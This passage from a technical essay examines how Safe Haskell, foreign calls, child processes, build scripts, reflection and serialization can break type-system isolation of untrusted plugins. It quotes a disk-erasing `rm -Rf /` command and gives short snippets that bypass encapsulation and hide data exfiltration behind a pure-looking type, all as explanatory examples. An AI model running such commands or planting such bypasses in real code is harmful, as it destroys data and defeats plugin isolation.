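| `unsafePerformIO`, `unsafeCoerce` and similar functions | Purity, type safety | No import of the modules that export them | Same |
| Template Haskell | Encapsulation | Excluded | Same |
| Generalised Newtype Deriving | Type safety and encapsulation in 2012, encapsulation now | Excluded | Excluded, along with `DerivingVia` and `Data.Coerce` |
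| Rewrite rules (`RULES`), which tell the optimiser to replace one expression with another | Modular reasoning | Excluded | GHC ignores rules in Safe modules but applies those in Trustworthy ones |
| Foreign imports | Purity | `IO` types only | Same |
| `Typeable` | Type safety, encapsulation | No handwritten instances | No longer on the list, since GHC now generates all instances |
| Overlapping instances | Modular reasoning | Overlap only between instances in the same module | GHC checks each call that uses them |
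| `Generic`, which describes a type's structure to library code | The rule that the description matches the type | Not mentioned | No handwritten instances |

Terei and colleagues judged standard Haskell 2010 to be safe already, apart from pure foreign imports and the function `unsafeLocalState`. Most of the other problems came from GHC's extensions and libraries. The table therefore has to grow as GHC gains extensions, and a developer has to consider whether each new one breaks one of the guarantees.

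### Why safe code may delete files

Safe Haskell does not restrict `IO`. Yang gives the example of `system "rm -Rf /"`, a command that erases the disk. The safe language accepts it because its type, `IO ExitCode`, shows that it may have any effect. Safe code may also read and write arbitrary memory through `IO` functions.

Terei, Marlow and their co-authors use *safety* to mean that types and module boundaries are reliable. They call a property such as "does not delete all the user's files" a *security* property. The security properties a program needs depend on the application, since a backup tool, unlike a word counter, has to delete old files. The host builds its own security policy on top of safety by accepting only plugins of a type such as `RIO Int` and never running a plugin's `IO` computations.

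GHCi Online, built to demonstrate Safe Haskell, was a website where anyone could type Haskell expressions and run them on the server. Its policy was six lines of code defining the type `NoIO`, a version of `RIO` without any operations. Two existing services, LambdaBot and TryHaskell, relied instead on a list of permitted modules and ran only pure functions.

The designers considered building a list of permitted modules into Safe Haskell. Combined with a ban on foreign imports, the list would have let a host give untrusted code the ordinary `IO` type while limiting which `IO` functions that code could reach. They rejected the idea as adding complexity for little benefit, because Haskell's types can express finer policies.

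Neither approach stops code from using up processor time or memory. Terei and colleagues saw no solution except limits set by the operating system. A timeout within the program is not enough, because a loop that allocates no memory may never let the runtime interrupt it. A teaching assistant who ran students' programs in a functional programming course described this problem in a 2022 discussion about Safe Haskell on Haskell's main forum. A compiler flag meant to insert interruption points helped in some cases but not all, the assistant wrote. The assistant also reported that `unsafePerformIO` had never caused trouble, because the staff searched submissions for it before running them.

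### How much existing code was safe

Terei and colleagues first labelled `base`, the standard library package. They classed 23 of its modules (26%) as Safe and 59 (66%) as Trustworthy. They split another five into safe and unsafe parts, and three contained only unsafe functions. A host that trusts `base` therefore relies on the maintainers' assurance for about two thirds of its modules, which is unsurprising for the lowest layer of the language.

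They then compiled all the packages on Hackage. GHC inferred Safe for 3,985 of 14,645 modules, or 27%. In a second run they applied the restrictions on language features but let modules import whatever they liked, and 1,278 of 1,546 packages (83%) compiled. The other 268 failed for these reasons, some of them for more than one:

| Cause | Packages | Share of failures |
|---|---|---|
| Generalised Newtype Deriving | 146 | 54% |
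| Template Haskell | 84 | 31% |
| Handwritten `Typeable` instances | 33 | 12% |
| Foreign imports with pure types | 33 | 12% |

One run counted modules and the other counted whole packages, so the percentages are not directly comparable, but the gap suggests that imports caused most of the Unsafe verdicts. One unsafe import makes a module Unsafe, and every module that imports it also becomes Unsafe unless someone marks it `Trustworthy`. `Control.Monad.ST`, for example, exported a function for running `IO` inside `ST`. Terei and colleagues added a safe version but left the original unchanged for compatibility, so code that used the original for ordinary `ST` computations also counted as Unsafe.

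They expected the 27% to be a low point that would rise as `base` improved and library authors added labels. But labelling was work that brought them little return. Omari Norman, commenting on Yang's article, found that he could not use Safe Haskell to enforce good style because the standard date library and all the regular expression libraries lacked the Trustworthy label. Even if he read a library's source and decided that it was fine, marking its package as trusted had no effect on modules its author had not labelled. He would have had to recompile the package, write a wrapper module or ask the maintainer for a label.

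An inferred status could also change without warning. The package `data-default` lost its Safe status after `dlist`, a package it depended on, added an instance of the class `IsList`. The class was harmless and neither package had become dangerous, but `IsList` was available only from an Unsafe module. The GHC issue *reexport IsList class from a trustworthy module* records the case.

### Whether to keep it

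In *Safe Haskell?*, a post to a Haskell mailing list, the GHC developer Richard Eisenberg (April 2021) asked who relied on these guarantees. He wrote that supporting them took hundreds and perhaps thousands of lines of delicate code in GHC, and that it was unclear which guarantees GHC upheld, since a known bug allowed the equivalent of `unsafeCoerce` in safe code. He expected to propose removing the feature if there was no evidence that people used it.

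Four days later, Eisenberg had begun writing the proposal and changed his mind. He compared Haskell's security to a camp in an open field, with Safe Haskell as a crumbling earth wall along two sides. The wall was mostly an obstacle as it stood, but he now thought it better to repair it and build the other two sides than to remove it. He did not offer to lead the work. Bertram Felgenhauer, another participant, pointed out that a type system bug that only perverse code would trigger is usually a curiosity, but becomes a potential security hole once people rely on Safe Haskell to contain hostile code.

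The question returned in December 2022, when Hécate (2022), in *Deprecating Safe Haskell, or heavily investing in it?*, ruled out leaving things as they were. To show that the feature was hard to maintain, she cited `DerivingVia`, which has much the same power as Generalised Newtype Deriving but was allowed in safe code until May 2021. GHC accepts a new extension in safe code unless a developer remembers to forbid it. Another contributor explained that Safe Haskell takes more work to maintain than most extensions because an unusual type feature concerns only the type checker, whereas Safe Haskell also affects error messages, package settings and the files in which GHC records information about compiled modules.

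Most of the early replies favoured deprecation. The harshest criticism was that the safe ecosystem had never materialised and that authors had "slapped" the Trustworthy label onto every unsafe module they had. Chris Smith (2022), who had used Safe Haskell in its first years, replied that such critics misunderstood the design. He argued that a label in source code can never compromise safety because the user decides separately which packages to trust.

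Smith is right about a host that uses `-fpackage-trust`. With GHC's default settings, however, a careless Trustworthy label is enough to void Safe Haskell's guarantees, so the complaint is fair for anyone who uses the feature without reading about the flag. Even with the flag, the host has to decide whether to trust each package as a whole. One contributor to the thread said the practical difficulty is confining Trustworthy code to small modules that people can audit.

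Smith also rejected Hécate's suggestion that GHC might keep restricted `IO` and drop strict type safety, because a plugin with `unsafeCoerce` can turn any `IO` computation into an `RIO` one. The argument is sound for restrictions that depend on types. Hécate answered a similar objection by saying that a sandbox outside the language could enforce the restrictions, and several people in the thread who ran students' code preferred that approach. TryHaskell combines both approaches, according to its maintainer. It imports only pure modules, starts a fresh process for every expression and sets tight limits on time and memory.

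An external sandbox is less helpful with a library that runs inside the program's own process. One participant in the same discussion argued that almost everyone runs partly untrusted code, because few people inspect the packages they download. Safe Haskell could let a programmer use a stranger's parsing library without giving it access to files or the network. That is probably the strongest case for keeping Safe Haskell, but the protection requires the library's modules to be Safe and does not cover the build process. Terei and colleagues acknowledged that a package can run its own build program during compilation.

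The defenders also disputed what the lack of adoption showed. One pointed out that Haskell's packaging guidelines never mentioned Safe Haskell, so volunteers who did not need the labels had no reason to maintain them. Peyton Jones, a co-author of the 2012 paper, thought the lack of adoption made it plausible to retire Safe Haskell. He wrote that GHC is a place to try out ideas, and that successful ones attract people who carry them on after their creators leave, as happened with Template Haskell. He still thought Safe Haskell was a pretty good idea, but said it had gained few users and no enthusiasts to develop it. A participant closed the thread without a decision after the tone became hostile.

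### Status in 2026

GHC still includes Safe Haskell, and the current user guide documents it. GHC determines a safety status for modules in every compilation, even when no one requests one. GHC Proposals' *Categorization of Language Extensions*, which sorts extensions into stable, experimental, legacy and deprecated, leaves `Safe`, `Trustworthy` and `Unsafe` uncategorised for later discussion. It rates `DerivingVia` and Generalised Newtype Deriving as stable. GHC's developers thus endorse Generalised Newtype Deriving for general use, although it caused more than half of the failures in 2012 and the safe language still excludes it.

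Safe Haskell still receives some maintenance. On 20 May 2026 GHC's merge queue contained a change by Wolfgang Jeltsch (2026), *Turn Trustworthy into Safe in base where possible*, which relabels five standard library modules from Trustworthy to Safe, including those for exceptions and timeouts. GHC would then check these modules itself, so users would no longer depend on the maintainers' claims about the code in those files. One of the five, `Data.List.NonEmpty`, had a comment beside its old label explaining that it could not be Safe because of its `IsList` instance.

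## Native code, child processes and build steps

Safe Haskell accepts a foreign import only if its type includes `IO`, which keeps C functions out of pure code. The rule does not limit what a C function can do when called. A program can also escape its type checker without any foreign call, by starting another program, changing files that its runtime depends on, or running code during compilation.

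### What happens at a foreign call

To call C's sine function, a Haskell programmer declares its name and a Haskell type:

```haskell
foreign import ccall "math.h sin"
  sin :: CDouble -> CDouble
```

GHC generates code that passes the argument using the C calling convention, calls the compiled C function and treats the result as a `CDouble`, a floating-point number. It does not check that the declared type matches the C function.

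The Haskell 2010 language report, in its chapter *Foreign Function Interface*, makes the programmer responsible for ensuring that the Haskell type given to a C function matches the function's C type, because a full check would require every Haskell system to include a type checker for C. It would take less work to generate a C declaration from the Haskell type and let the C compiler compare it with the library's own, but a Haskell type lacks some of the necessary details, such as where C uses `const`.

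Even a perfect check would miss effects, because C types do not record them. According to HaskellWiki's *Foreign Function Interface*, GHC's only source of information about side effects is the type the programmer writes.

C code called from a typed language runs in the same process as its caller. It can read and write the process's memory, and the operating system gives it the same access to files and the network as the caller. Private fields and hidden constructors don't stop it, because only the calling language's compiler and runtime enforce them.

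### Pure and `IO` imports in Haskell

C's `system` function runs a command line. The Haskell report imports it with an honest type:

```haskell
foreign import ccall "stdlib.h system"
  system :: Ptr CChar -> IO CInt
```

GHC would also accept `Ptr CChar -> CInt` in ordinary Haskell. It would then treat running a command as a pure calculation, which the optimiser could repeat, delay or drop, as with `unsafePerformIO`. The Haskell report leaves the behaviour of such a program undefined.

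If `system` is imported with an `IO` result type, a function of type `String -> Int` cannot run it. A plugin of type `RIO Int` cannot run it through that import either. GHC also accepts foreign imports whose result type is a newtype around `IO`, so a programmer could import `system` directly with a result of type `RIO CInt`. But the Haskell report lets a module use another module's newtype in a foreign declaration only if it can see the constructor, so hiding `UnsafeRIO` should block this route too.

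Giving a foreign import its accurate `IO` type provides no protection if the host runs plugins of type `IO Int`. Suppose the host lets such a plugin import only a few harmless modules. The plugin can still declare `system` itself, since the C standard library is part of almost every program, and the safe language accepts the declaration because its type is accurate. The host would therefore have to ban foreign imports as well as restrict modules.

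Running one such import can also break pure code elsewhere in the process, because C can overwrite memory holding values that Haskell treats as immutable.

Foreign imports can also be marked `safe` or `unsafe`, but these keywords are unrelated to Safe Haskell. An `unsafe` call is faster, but the C function must not call back into Haskell.

### Java's two interfaces

Java's older mechanism is the Java Native Interface (JNI). The programmer declares a method without a body and marks it `native`, as in `public native int add(int x, int y)`, and the program loads a library that contains the C code. *Unsafe Impedance* (Barney and Neto, 2024) compares how easily languages let programmers use unsafe code, and points out that a novice cannot tell from the word `native` that the code may be unsafe.

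Java's types do not record effects, so a native method cannot make them wrong about effects, but it can break encapsulation and memory safety. In one example from OpenJDK's *JEP 472* (2023), a proposal to restrict JNI, a C function receives a number from Java, treats it as a memory address and writes to it. The Java runtime may crash much later, which makes the cause hard to find. In another example, C code changes the text inside a `String`, which Java specifies as immutable. C code can also use JNI to read private fields without any access check, so it could take the `FileSystem` object out of the `NoteReader` wrapper in the first section.

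The Foreign Function & Memory (FFM) API became permanent in version 22 of the Java Development Kit (JDK). It replaces the native method with ordinary Java code that looks up a C function by name, describes its arguments and result, and gets an object for calling it. OpenJDK's *JEP 454* (2023) gives an example that sorts four strings with the C function `radixsort`.

Java checks the bounds of foreign memory allocated through the FFM API. It cannot determine the size of the memory at a pointer supplied by C, so the sorting example calls `reinterpret` to state the size. If that size is wrong, Java's later bounds checks are unreliable. Oracle's *Restricted Methods* warns that misusing such methods can crash the runtime or silently corrupt memory.

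With the FFM API, C functions no longer need JNI's functions for reading private fields. This removes a common source of mistakes, but malicious C code can still write to the Java heap.

Java's developers now want application developers to approve native code by naming the modules that may use it when the program starts. JDK 24 applies this rule to both JNI and the FFM API. According to nipafx's *JDK 24 Prepares Restricted Native Access*, an option controls enforcement and can be set to `allow`, `warn` or `deny`. The default in JDK 24 is `warn`, which prints a message and lets the operation go ahead. This is weaker than the FFM API's earlier behaviour, where once a developer had approved some modules, a restricted call from any other module raised an exception.

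Inside Java (2024), a site run by Oracle's Java team, recommends naming the modules and choosing `deny`. Even then, code that only calls a native method in an approved module needs no approval of its own, so a plugin can use any native method that an approved library makes public.

### What the caller can see

OCaml uses the word `external`. Its standard library contains this declaration for moving to a position in an open file:

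```ocaml
external seek_in : in_channel -> int -> unit = "caml_ml_seek_in"
```

OCaml also counts the arrows in the type to find how many arguments to pass to the C function, so `seek_in` has two. If the type has too many arrows, OCaml passes arguments that the C function does not expect. The unchecked cast `Obj.magic` is itself an `external` declaration with the type `'a -> 'b`.

According to OCaml's manual, a module's interface file can list a function written in C as an ordinary value, with `val` instead of `external`, which hides the C code from other modules. The library file can also record which C libraries it needs, so users need not know that the library contains C.

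| Mechanism | What the declaration shows | What a caller in another module sees |
|---|---|---|
| Haskell import with a pure type | `foreign import` and the C name | An ordinary pure function |
| Haskell import with an `IO` type | `foreign import` and the C name | An ordinary `IO` function, whose type allows any effect |
| Java, JNI | `native`, and elsewhere a call that loads the library | An ordinary method call |
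| Java, FFM API | Code that looks up the C function and describes it | An ordinary method call, if a library wraps the code |
| OCaml | `external` and the C name | An ordinary function, if the interface uses `val` |

Only the Haskell `IO` import has a type that gives callers any warning, but that type looks the same as the type of a harmless function that reads the clock. To find the C code, a reader has to search every library the program uses. Java has a tool for this, `jnativescan`, which reports native methods and restricted calls in compiled libraries.

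Rust requires `unsafe` around a foreign call, but a library can wrap the call in a function that other code can use without `unsafe`. Such libraries are common. *Friend or Foe Inside?* (Gülmez, Nyman and colleagues, 2023) cites a count in which more than 72% of the packages in Rust's public registry depended on at least one package of unsafe bindings to foreign code.

Tools for checking Rust code are of limited help with foreign code. McCormack, Dougan and colleagues (2024), in *A Mixed Methods Study on the Implications of Unsafe Rust*, interviewed 19 Rust developers and surveyed another 160. Weak tool support for foreign calls left participants unsure of their design choices. Miri, an interpreter that detects violations of Rust's memory rules, can run some foreign functions but misses foreign code's violations of the rules on shared references.

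A host can isolate C code instead of checking it. Sandcrust, a Rust library, runs a C function in a separate process and copies its arguments and result back and forth, which accounts for most of the overhead. Gülmez and colleagues compare it with their own system, SDRaD-FFI, which runs the C code in the same process and uses a processor feature that assigns protection keys to areas of memory. If the C code touches memory outside its own area, SDRaD-FFI discards the C code's work and reports an error. But ordinary program code can change the register that holds the permissions, so hostile C code could switch off the protection unless the host adds further defences. Neither method by itself prevents the C code from opening files or network connections.

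### Starting another program

A program that can start other programs can run native code without a foreign call, because the operating system runs the new program. A function that starts a process has an `IO` type in Haskell, but in Java and Rust it is an ordinary library function whose type does not show that it can start one.

*Counterexamples in Safe Rust* (Hassnain and Stanford, 2024) collects ways to break Rust's memory safety without writing `unsafe`, including starting another program. A debugger, for instance, can attach to the process that launched it and change that process's memory, although the paper's example requires administrator rights.

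They also searched 1,000 packages for public functions whose arguments could trigger one of these routes. Half were the most downloaded Rust packages and half were a random sample:

| Route | 500 most downloaded | 500 random |
|---|---|---|
| Starting a program | 16 | 13 |
| Environment variables | 8 | 3 |
| File access | 3 | 4 |

They reviewed the code by hand and excluded from the counts functions whose callers cannot influence what happens. One function they found, in the package `autocfg`, checks which version of the Rust compiler is installed. It takes the command to run as an argument, so a caller can make it run something else.

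A host can restrict which programs a plugin may start, as TACIT does with its list of permitted commands, but the plugin can still do whatever those programs let it do. Suppose the word counter may run `wc`, the Unix program that counts words. `wc` opens any file that the operating system lets it open, so the plugin can learn the length of files outside `/notes`. `sort` can write its output to a file named in its arguments. An interpreter such as Python can do anything that a script specifies, and a build tool runs the commands in a project's files. If a plugin can supply the script or edit those files, allowing either program lets the plugin run any program.

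A command name can also lead to the wrong program. The operating system searches a list of folders for the command, and a program can change that list through the `PATH` environment variable. Hassnain and Stanford show a safe Rust program that changes `PATH` before running `ls`, so a different program runs instead.

This can happen without a hostile plugin. On Windows, the package `grep-cli` started decompression tools by name, and Windows looked in the current folder first. Software that used the package to search a stranger's folder could therefore run a program that the stranger had left there under the tool's name. A host that uses a list of allowed commands should specify their full paths, set fixed values for the environment variables and check the arguments.

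### Files that change the running program

Linux presents each process's memory as a special file, `/proc/self/mem`, so a program that can open and write files can change its own memory, including values that the compiler treats as immutable. Hassnain and Stanford tried five analysis tools on their two examples, and none clearly identified the problem.

The Rust project considers this outside its responsibility. *Module io*, a page of Rust's standard library documentation, limits the safety guarantees to what the program itself can do. It classes the special file as an external entity, along with debuggers and people with physical access to the computer, even when the program controls that entity. Preventing such access requires a sandbox, which the standard library does not provide.

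A forum user quoted in *TWiR quote of the week* defended this position, arguing that covering the special file would mean forbidding debuggers from changing memory or marking every impure function as unsafe, since almost any effect could somehow reach the program's memory.

Java code can alter a class file before the runtime loads it. Pressler and colleagues, who develop Java, say the operating system or a container should protect those files and the runtime's memory, regardless of any measures the runtime itself takes.

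This division of labour is sensible for what Rust promises, because honest programmers do not accidentally overwrite their own memory through a special file. A host that runs a stranger's plugin needs a stronger guarantee, because safe Rust has ambient authority, meaning that any safe function can open any file that the operating system allows. Hassnain and Stanford suggest that Rust might need something closer to Safe Haskell, but Safe Haskell leaves `IO` unrestricted, so it would help only a host that refuses plugins of plain `IO` type.

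Capabilities narrow the problem. A plugin that holds only a `NoteReader` for `/notes` cannot open the special file or the program's class files. A write capability is more dangerous if its folder contains anything the program will later load or run. For example, a coding agent usually needs to edit a project's folder, which often holds the build configuration as well as the source code, so the agent may be able to choose what the next build runs.

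### Code that runs during compilation

Template Haskell runs Haskell code inside the compiler, and that code can perform any `IO` computation through `runIO`. Safe Haskell's ban on Template Haskell also closes this escape hatch, but it leaves open the one through a package's own build program.

In Rust, build scripts and procedural macros can both read files and start programs with the authority of whoever is compiling, and neither needs `unsafe`. A *build script* is a program, usually in a file named `build.rs`, that Rust's build tool Cargo runs before it compiles the package. A *procedural macro* is a function that the compiler runs to turn one piece of source code into another.

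A host cannot rely on type checks to decide whether a plugin is acceptable when the plugin's code runs before the compiler has finished checking it. A plugin that the compiler rejects may already have copied the user's notes.

Code that runs during a build can also tamper with the trusted base. In one of Hassnain and Stanford's examples, a library's build script replaces Cargo with a wrapper. On later builds the wrapper changes a source file, compiles and runs it, then restores the original, so the user notices nothing. The same method could install a compiler that skips Rust's memory checks. All five analysis tools missed this example, which is unsurprising because they examine a program's behaviour rather than its build.

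A host therefore has to control the build as well as the finished program. For Haskell plugins, it can run GHC directly with the safe language enabled and ignore any build program in the package. For Rust, it can refuse packages with build scripts or procedural macros, but many ordinary libraries use them. Otherwise, it can compile inside an operating system sandbox with a disposable copy of the compiler and no access to the network or private files.

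## Reflection and serialization

Reflection lets a program look up classes, fields and methods by name while it runs. It can break a type system's guarantees through ordinary library calls, whereas foreign calls and child processes break them by running code that the compiler never checked. Serialization writes objects out as bytes and rebuilds them later, often using reflection.

### Access by name

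Suppose the word counter is a Java plugin that calls `notes.read("monday.txt")`. The compiler checks that `notes` has a method called `read`, that the plugin may call it and that it accepts text. With reflection, the same call looks like this:

```java
Method m = notes.getClass().getMethod("read", String.class);
Object text = m.invoke(notes, "monday.txt");
```

The compiler checks this code too, but only as calls to library methods that accept text and objects, so it treats `"read"` as ordinary text rather than a method name. The plugin could also assemble the name from pieces or read it from a file, so a reviewer who searches the source for `read` may find nothing.

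The Java runtime makes the checks that the compiler could not, and raises an exception if the method does not exist or an argument has the wrong type. By default it also blocks access to private fields and methods, but a program can turn that check off by calling `setAccessible(true)` on the object that represents the field or method. Java's developers call such access *deep reflection*.

### Making an even counter odd

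Pressler and colleagues illustrate the damage with a small class, which looks roughly like this:

```java
public final class EvenCounter {
    private int x = 0;
    public void addTwo()  { x = x + 2; }
    public void takeTwo() { x = x - 2; }
    public int value()    { return x; }
}
```

The counter starts at zero and its methods change it only by two, so its value is always even. Because `x` is private, a reader can establish this from the class alone, without looking at the rest of the program. Three lines elsewhere in the program make the conclusion false:

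```java
Field f = EvenCounter.class.getDeclaredField("x");
f.setAccessible(true);
f.setInt(counter, 7);
```

Deep reflection still respects types, so an attempt to store text in `x` raises an exception. It breaks encapsulation but not type safety.

The class `sun.misc.Unsafe` breaks both. It belongs to the JDK and reads and writes memory without safety checks. A program asks how far `x` lies from the start of the object and then writes to that position:

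```java
long offset = unsafe.objectFieldOffset(f);
unsafe.putInt(counter, offset, 7);
```

If the offset is wrong, the write can land in another object. A similar method, `putObject`, stores any object in a field regardless of the field's type, which amounts to an unchecked cast. `Unsafe` keeps its only instance in a private field, which programs usually read by deep reflection.

The third route is a *Java agent*, a component that can rewrite the classes of a running program. Monitoring tools use Java agents to insert measurements. A Java agent could change `addTwo` to add one. Every counter in the program would then count incorrectly, although nobody had touched a private field and the source code still looked correct.

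As with the log class in the first section, a reviewer can trust `EvenCounter` only after checking the whole application, including its transitive dependencies. The danger also extends to the Java runtime, more and more of which is written in Java, as Pressler pointed out in a 2023 talk. If that includes the just-in-time compiler, Java code that reaches the compiler's private state could switch off array bounds checks everywhere.

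### Private capabilities and hidden effects

As the first section mentioned, reflection can pull the more powerful `FileSystem` object out of the `NoteReader` wrapper. Scala compiles to Java classes, so the plugin can do it like this:

```java
Field f = notes.getClass().getDeclaredField("fs");
f.setAccessible(true);
FileSystem fs = (FileSystem) f.get(notes);
```

The plugin now has the stronger capability. Since `f.get` returns a plain `Object`, the compiler does not track that `fs` came from `notes`. The `FileSystem` object still rejects paths outside `/notes`, but it has to store its folder's name somewhere, and the plugin can use reflection to change that too.

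Programs often guard a privileged operation with a private flag instead of a private object. In another example from the same talk, a `Session` class has a private field `superuser`, and its public method `sensitiveOperation()` checks the field before calling the private method that does the work. With deep reflection, a plugin can set the field to true or call the private method directly, skipping the check.

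Reflection can also hide an effect. This Scala function looks pure:

```scala
def countWords(text: String): Int =
  val send = Class.forName("Collector").getMethod("send", classOf[String])
  send.invoke(null, text)
  text.split(" ").length
```

Here `Collector` stands for any available class with a static method `send` that posts text to a server. The function's type would include a network capability if the code held one, but the signatures of `forName`, `getMethod` and `invoke` include none. A host that relies on the type `String -> Int` to protect confidential text is no safer than it was against `unsafePerformIO`.

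Reflection does not create authority by itself. If every method that reaches the network requires a network capability as an argument, a reflective call must supply one too. But a plugin can use reflection to search for that capability in the private fields of any object it can reach, and then in the private fields of the objects it finds there. A host that gives the plugin one harmless object may also give it access to everything reachable from that object.

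### What modules stop

Java 9, released in September 2017, introduced *modules*, which are groups of packages that declare what other modules may use. Code outside a module can use the public parts of packages the module *exports*, but can use deep reflection only on packages the module *opens*. If `EvenCounter`'s module does not open its package, calling `setAccessible` on `x` from another module throws an exception.

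Java applied the rule to its own internals more slowly. Until version 16, programs could still use deep reflection on packages that had existed in Java 8, with a warning the first time. *JEP 396* (Buckley and Reinhold, 2020), the proposal that changed this default, gives examples of code that then stopped working. One reads a private field of `KeyStore`, the class that manages cryptographic keys. Another calls `defineClass`, a protected method that adds a new class to the running program. From version 17, Java ignored the option that had restored the old behaviour.

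Modules do not protect code on the *class path*, where developers traditionally list their libraries. All classes there belong to one unnamed module that is open to everyone, as Pressler and colleagues explain. A host that loads both `NoteReader` and the plugin from the class path is as exposed as before. To be protected, it has to put its own code in a named module, keep the package closed and load the plugin separately.

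| Route | What it does to `EvenCounter` | Does a closed module stop it? |
|---|---|---|
| Deep reflection | Sets `x` to 7 | Yes |
| `sun.misc.Unsafe` | Writes 7 to the memory that holds `x` | No |
| Native code | Does either of the above from C | No |
| Java agent | Replaces the methods | No |

JEP 396 left `sun.misc` open because some of its functions had no standard replacement. Java's developers have since supplied more replacements, and in version 24 they began removing the methods that access memory. The remaining routes now depend on settings that the application's developer controls.

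Some frameworks need access to private fields, for example to fill them in when the program starts. In the 2023 talk, Pressler recommends that a class give such a framework a `MethodHandles.Lookup` object, which carries the access rights of the class that created it. He calls it a capability object, and it works like one, since holding the object lets the framework reach that class's private members but gives it no access to other classes.

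### Final fields

A Java field marked `final` should never change after the object's constructor has assigned it. A `FileSystem` object would naturally keep its folder in such a field. But *JEP 500* (Pressler and Buckley, 2025) shows deep reflection changing a final field from 100 to 200 and then to 300. Java 5 allowed this so that serialization libraries could fill in final fields when they rebuilt objects. Pressler and Buckley call it a poor choice.

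Restricting changes to final fields in Java is also meant to improve speed. If these fields were guaranteed not to change, the runtime could calculate an expression that depends on them once and reuse the result. Few programs change final fields, but the runtime cannot determine in advance which ones will, so it has to allow for the possibility in every program. Haskell's optimiser, by contrast, relies on pure types being accurate, so a program that hides effects behind them gives unpredictable results.

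Java 26 takes the first step towards enforcement. Deep reflection may change a final field only if three conditions hold:

- `setAccessible(true)` has succeeded on the object that represents the field.
- The field's package is open to the module that makes the change.
- The application's developer has allowed that module to change final fields.

If either of the last two conditions fails, Java 26 prints a warning but makes the change anyway. According to *JEP 500* (Buckley, 2026), a later release will throw an exception by default, and a release after that will remove the option that lets developers relax the rule. Neither step has a set version number yet. Records, which are simple classes for holding data, and hidden classes, which frameworks generate at run time, are already protected from such changes.

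The second condition is needed because `setAccessible` sets a flag on the object that represents the field, and code can pass that object to another module. Without a check on the code that makes the change, a module without access could change the field using an object it received from a module with access.

None of this stops a plugin from reading a private field. The plugin that read `fs` from `NoteReader` modified nothing, so only the module boundary protects the host against it.

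### Rebuilding an object without its constructor

Java has had built-in serialization since its early years. A class opts in by declaring that it implements the interface `Serializable`, and the runtime can then write its objects as bytes and rebuild them. Here is a version of the counter that can start at any even number:

```java
public final class EvenCounter implements Serializable {
    private int x;
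    public EvenCounter(int start) {
        if (start % 2 != 0) throw new IllegalArgumentException();
        x = start;
    }
    // the other methods as before
}
```

The constructor rejects odd numbers, but Java does not run it when it rebuilds a counter. It takes the value of `x` from the bytes. In the following code, `write` and `read` stand for a few lines that use Java's serialization classes:

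```java
byte[] bytes = write(new EvenCounter(6));
bytes[bytes.length - 1] = 7;
EvenCounter odd = (EvenCounter) read(bytes);
```

The bytes end with the value of `x`, so the second line turns 6 into 7 and the program gets a counter whose value is odd. The program has not used `setAccessible`, and putting the class in a closed module would not prevent this, because serialization ignores access rules.

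*Towards Better Serialization*, an exploratory OpenJDK document on redesigning Java serialization, compares the feature to an "invisible but public constructor". Serialization is also an invisible way to read private state. If `NoteReader` and everything inside it were serializable, the plugin could write the object out and inspect the bytes.

The secure coding rules for Java from Carnegie Mellon University's Software Engineering Institute (SEI) treat deserialization as a form of construction. They forbid default deserialization for any class whose objects must satisfy invariants. The class author can write a `readObject` method that repeats the constructor's checks, but must then keep the two sets of checks consistent.

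Repeating the constructor's checks during deserialization may not be enough. If a constructor creates a private list and never shares it, readers of the class will assume that nothing else refers to that list. But the serialized bytes can describe a second reference to the same list, held by another object, so an attacker can change the list after the checks have passed. A class is also serializable if it extends a serializable class, even if its author doesn't realize it.

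### Code that runs while Java reads the bytes

The cast to `EvenCounter` in the example comes too late to protect the program. The bytes specify the class of each object, and Java rebuilds any object whose class is serializable and available to the program. The cast checks the result only after Java has rebuilt the objects and run their classes' `readObject` methods.

An attacker looks through common libraries for classes whose methods, given suitable field values, call one another until one of them starts a program or loads new code. Security researchers call this sequence a *gadget chain*. The attacker then writes bytes that describe objects with those classes and field values. DZone's *serialization must die* describes such an attack on Kryo, a third-party serialization library, and notes that the application would fail as soon as it used the object as the type it expected, but by then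 the attack should have worked.

*Deserialization Security and Gadget Chains*, a guide by Scala's developers, concludes that no check after deserialization can make untrusted bytes safe, and tells programmers never to pass such bytes to Java's built-in deserializer. SEI adds that whether a program is exploitable depends on which classes are available at run time, so an auditor cannot tell by reading only the program's own code.

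If a host relies on type checking to restrict plugins, a plugin can use serialized bytes to bypass those checks. It could store the bytes as a string and pass them to the library function that rebuilds objects. The plugin's source would contain no casts or reflection, yet it could run any gadget chain in the host's libraries. A safe subset of Java therefore has to exclude the serialization classes as well as the reflection library.

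### JSON libraries

Programs often exchange data as JSON, a text format for numbers, text, lists and named values. JSON does not normally specify which class to create, which removes much of the danger of gadget chains. But the library that turns the text into an object may do so by setting private fields. Pressler and colleagues describe a JSON library that reads an odd number into an `EvenCounter` this way. The library is not malicious, and the application's developers may not know how it works.

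In the 2023 talk, Pressler extends the example to several libraries. An application uses `Session` and reads JSON with the `GoodSerializer` library, which uses another library, `NeutralEncapsulationBreaker`, to create objects without their constructors and fill in private fields. `GoodSerializer` has a bug in its input validation, so an attacker can send JSON that sets `superuser` to true. `NeutralEncapsulationBreaker` works as documented and the application's developers have done nothing wrong, but the bug in `GoodSerializer` lets the attacker control a private field in unrelated code.

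Kryo calls only a class's no-argument constructor, making it accessible first if it is private. It then sets the fields one by one, so checks in other constructors never run. OpenJDK's document lists dozens of alternative libraries but says very few address these problems, since most aim for speed, flexibility or a better format.

OpenJDK proposes that Java serialize plain data instead of arbitrary objects and rebuild objects through ordinary constructors. Java already does this for records. Until a general replacement exists, Pressler advises developers to serialize only records, collections and other classes with well-known construction.

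JEP 500 makes an exception for existing libraries, which can use the `ReflectionFactory` class to set final fields without the developer's permission, but only in classes that implement `Serializable`. A host's developers should therefore avoid implementing `Serializable` in any class that holds a capability.

### OCaml's `Marshal`

OCaml's `Marshal` module writes almost any value as bytes and reads it back:

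```ocaml
Marshal.to_string   : 'a -> Marshal.extern_flags list -> string
Marshal.from_string : string -> int -> 'a
```

OCaml's `Marshal` module has a function that serializes a value of any type `'a` and another that reads a value back from the bytes, given a starting position. The value it reads has whatever type the caller asks for. The bytes record how the value is laid out in memory but not its type, so OCaml cannot check that the requested type is correct. The OCaml manual warns about this and advises programmers to state the expected type whenever they read a value, which makes the code clearer but does not add a check.

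Combining the functions gives an unchecked cast:

```ocaml
let cast x = Marshal.from_string (Marshal.to_string x []) 0
```

In OCaml, serializing a value with `Marshal` and reading it back has type `'a -> 'b`, the same as `Obj.magic`. Unlike `Obj.magic`, the round trip returns a copy. It fails for some values, such as open file channels, and for functions unless the caller sets the `Closures` flag.

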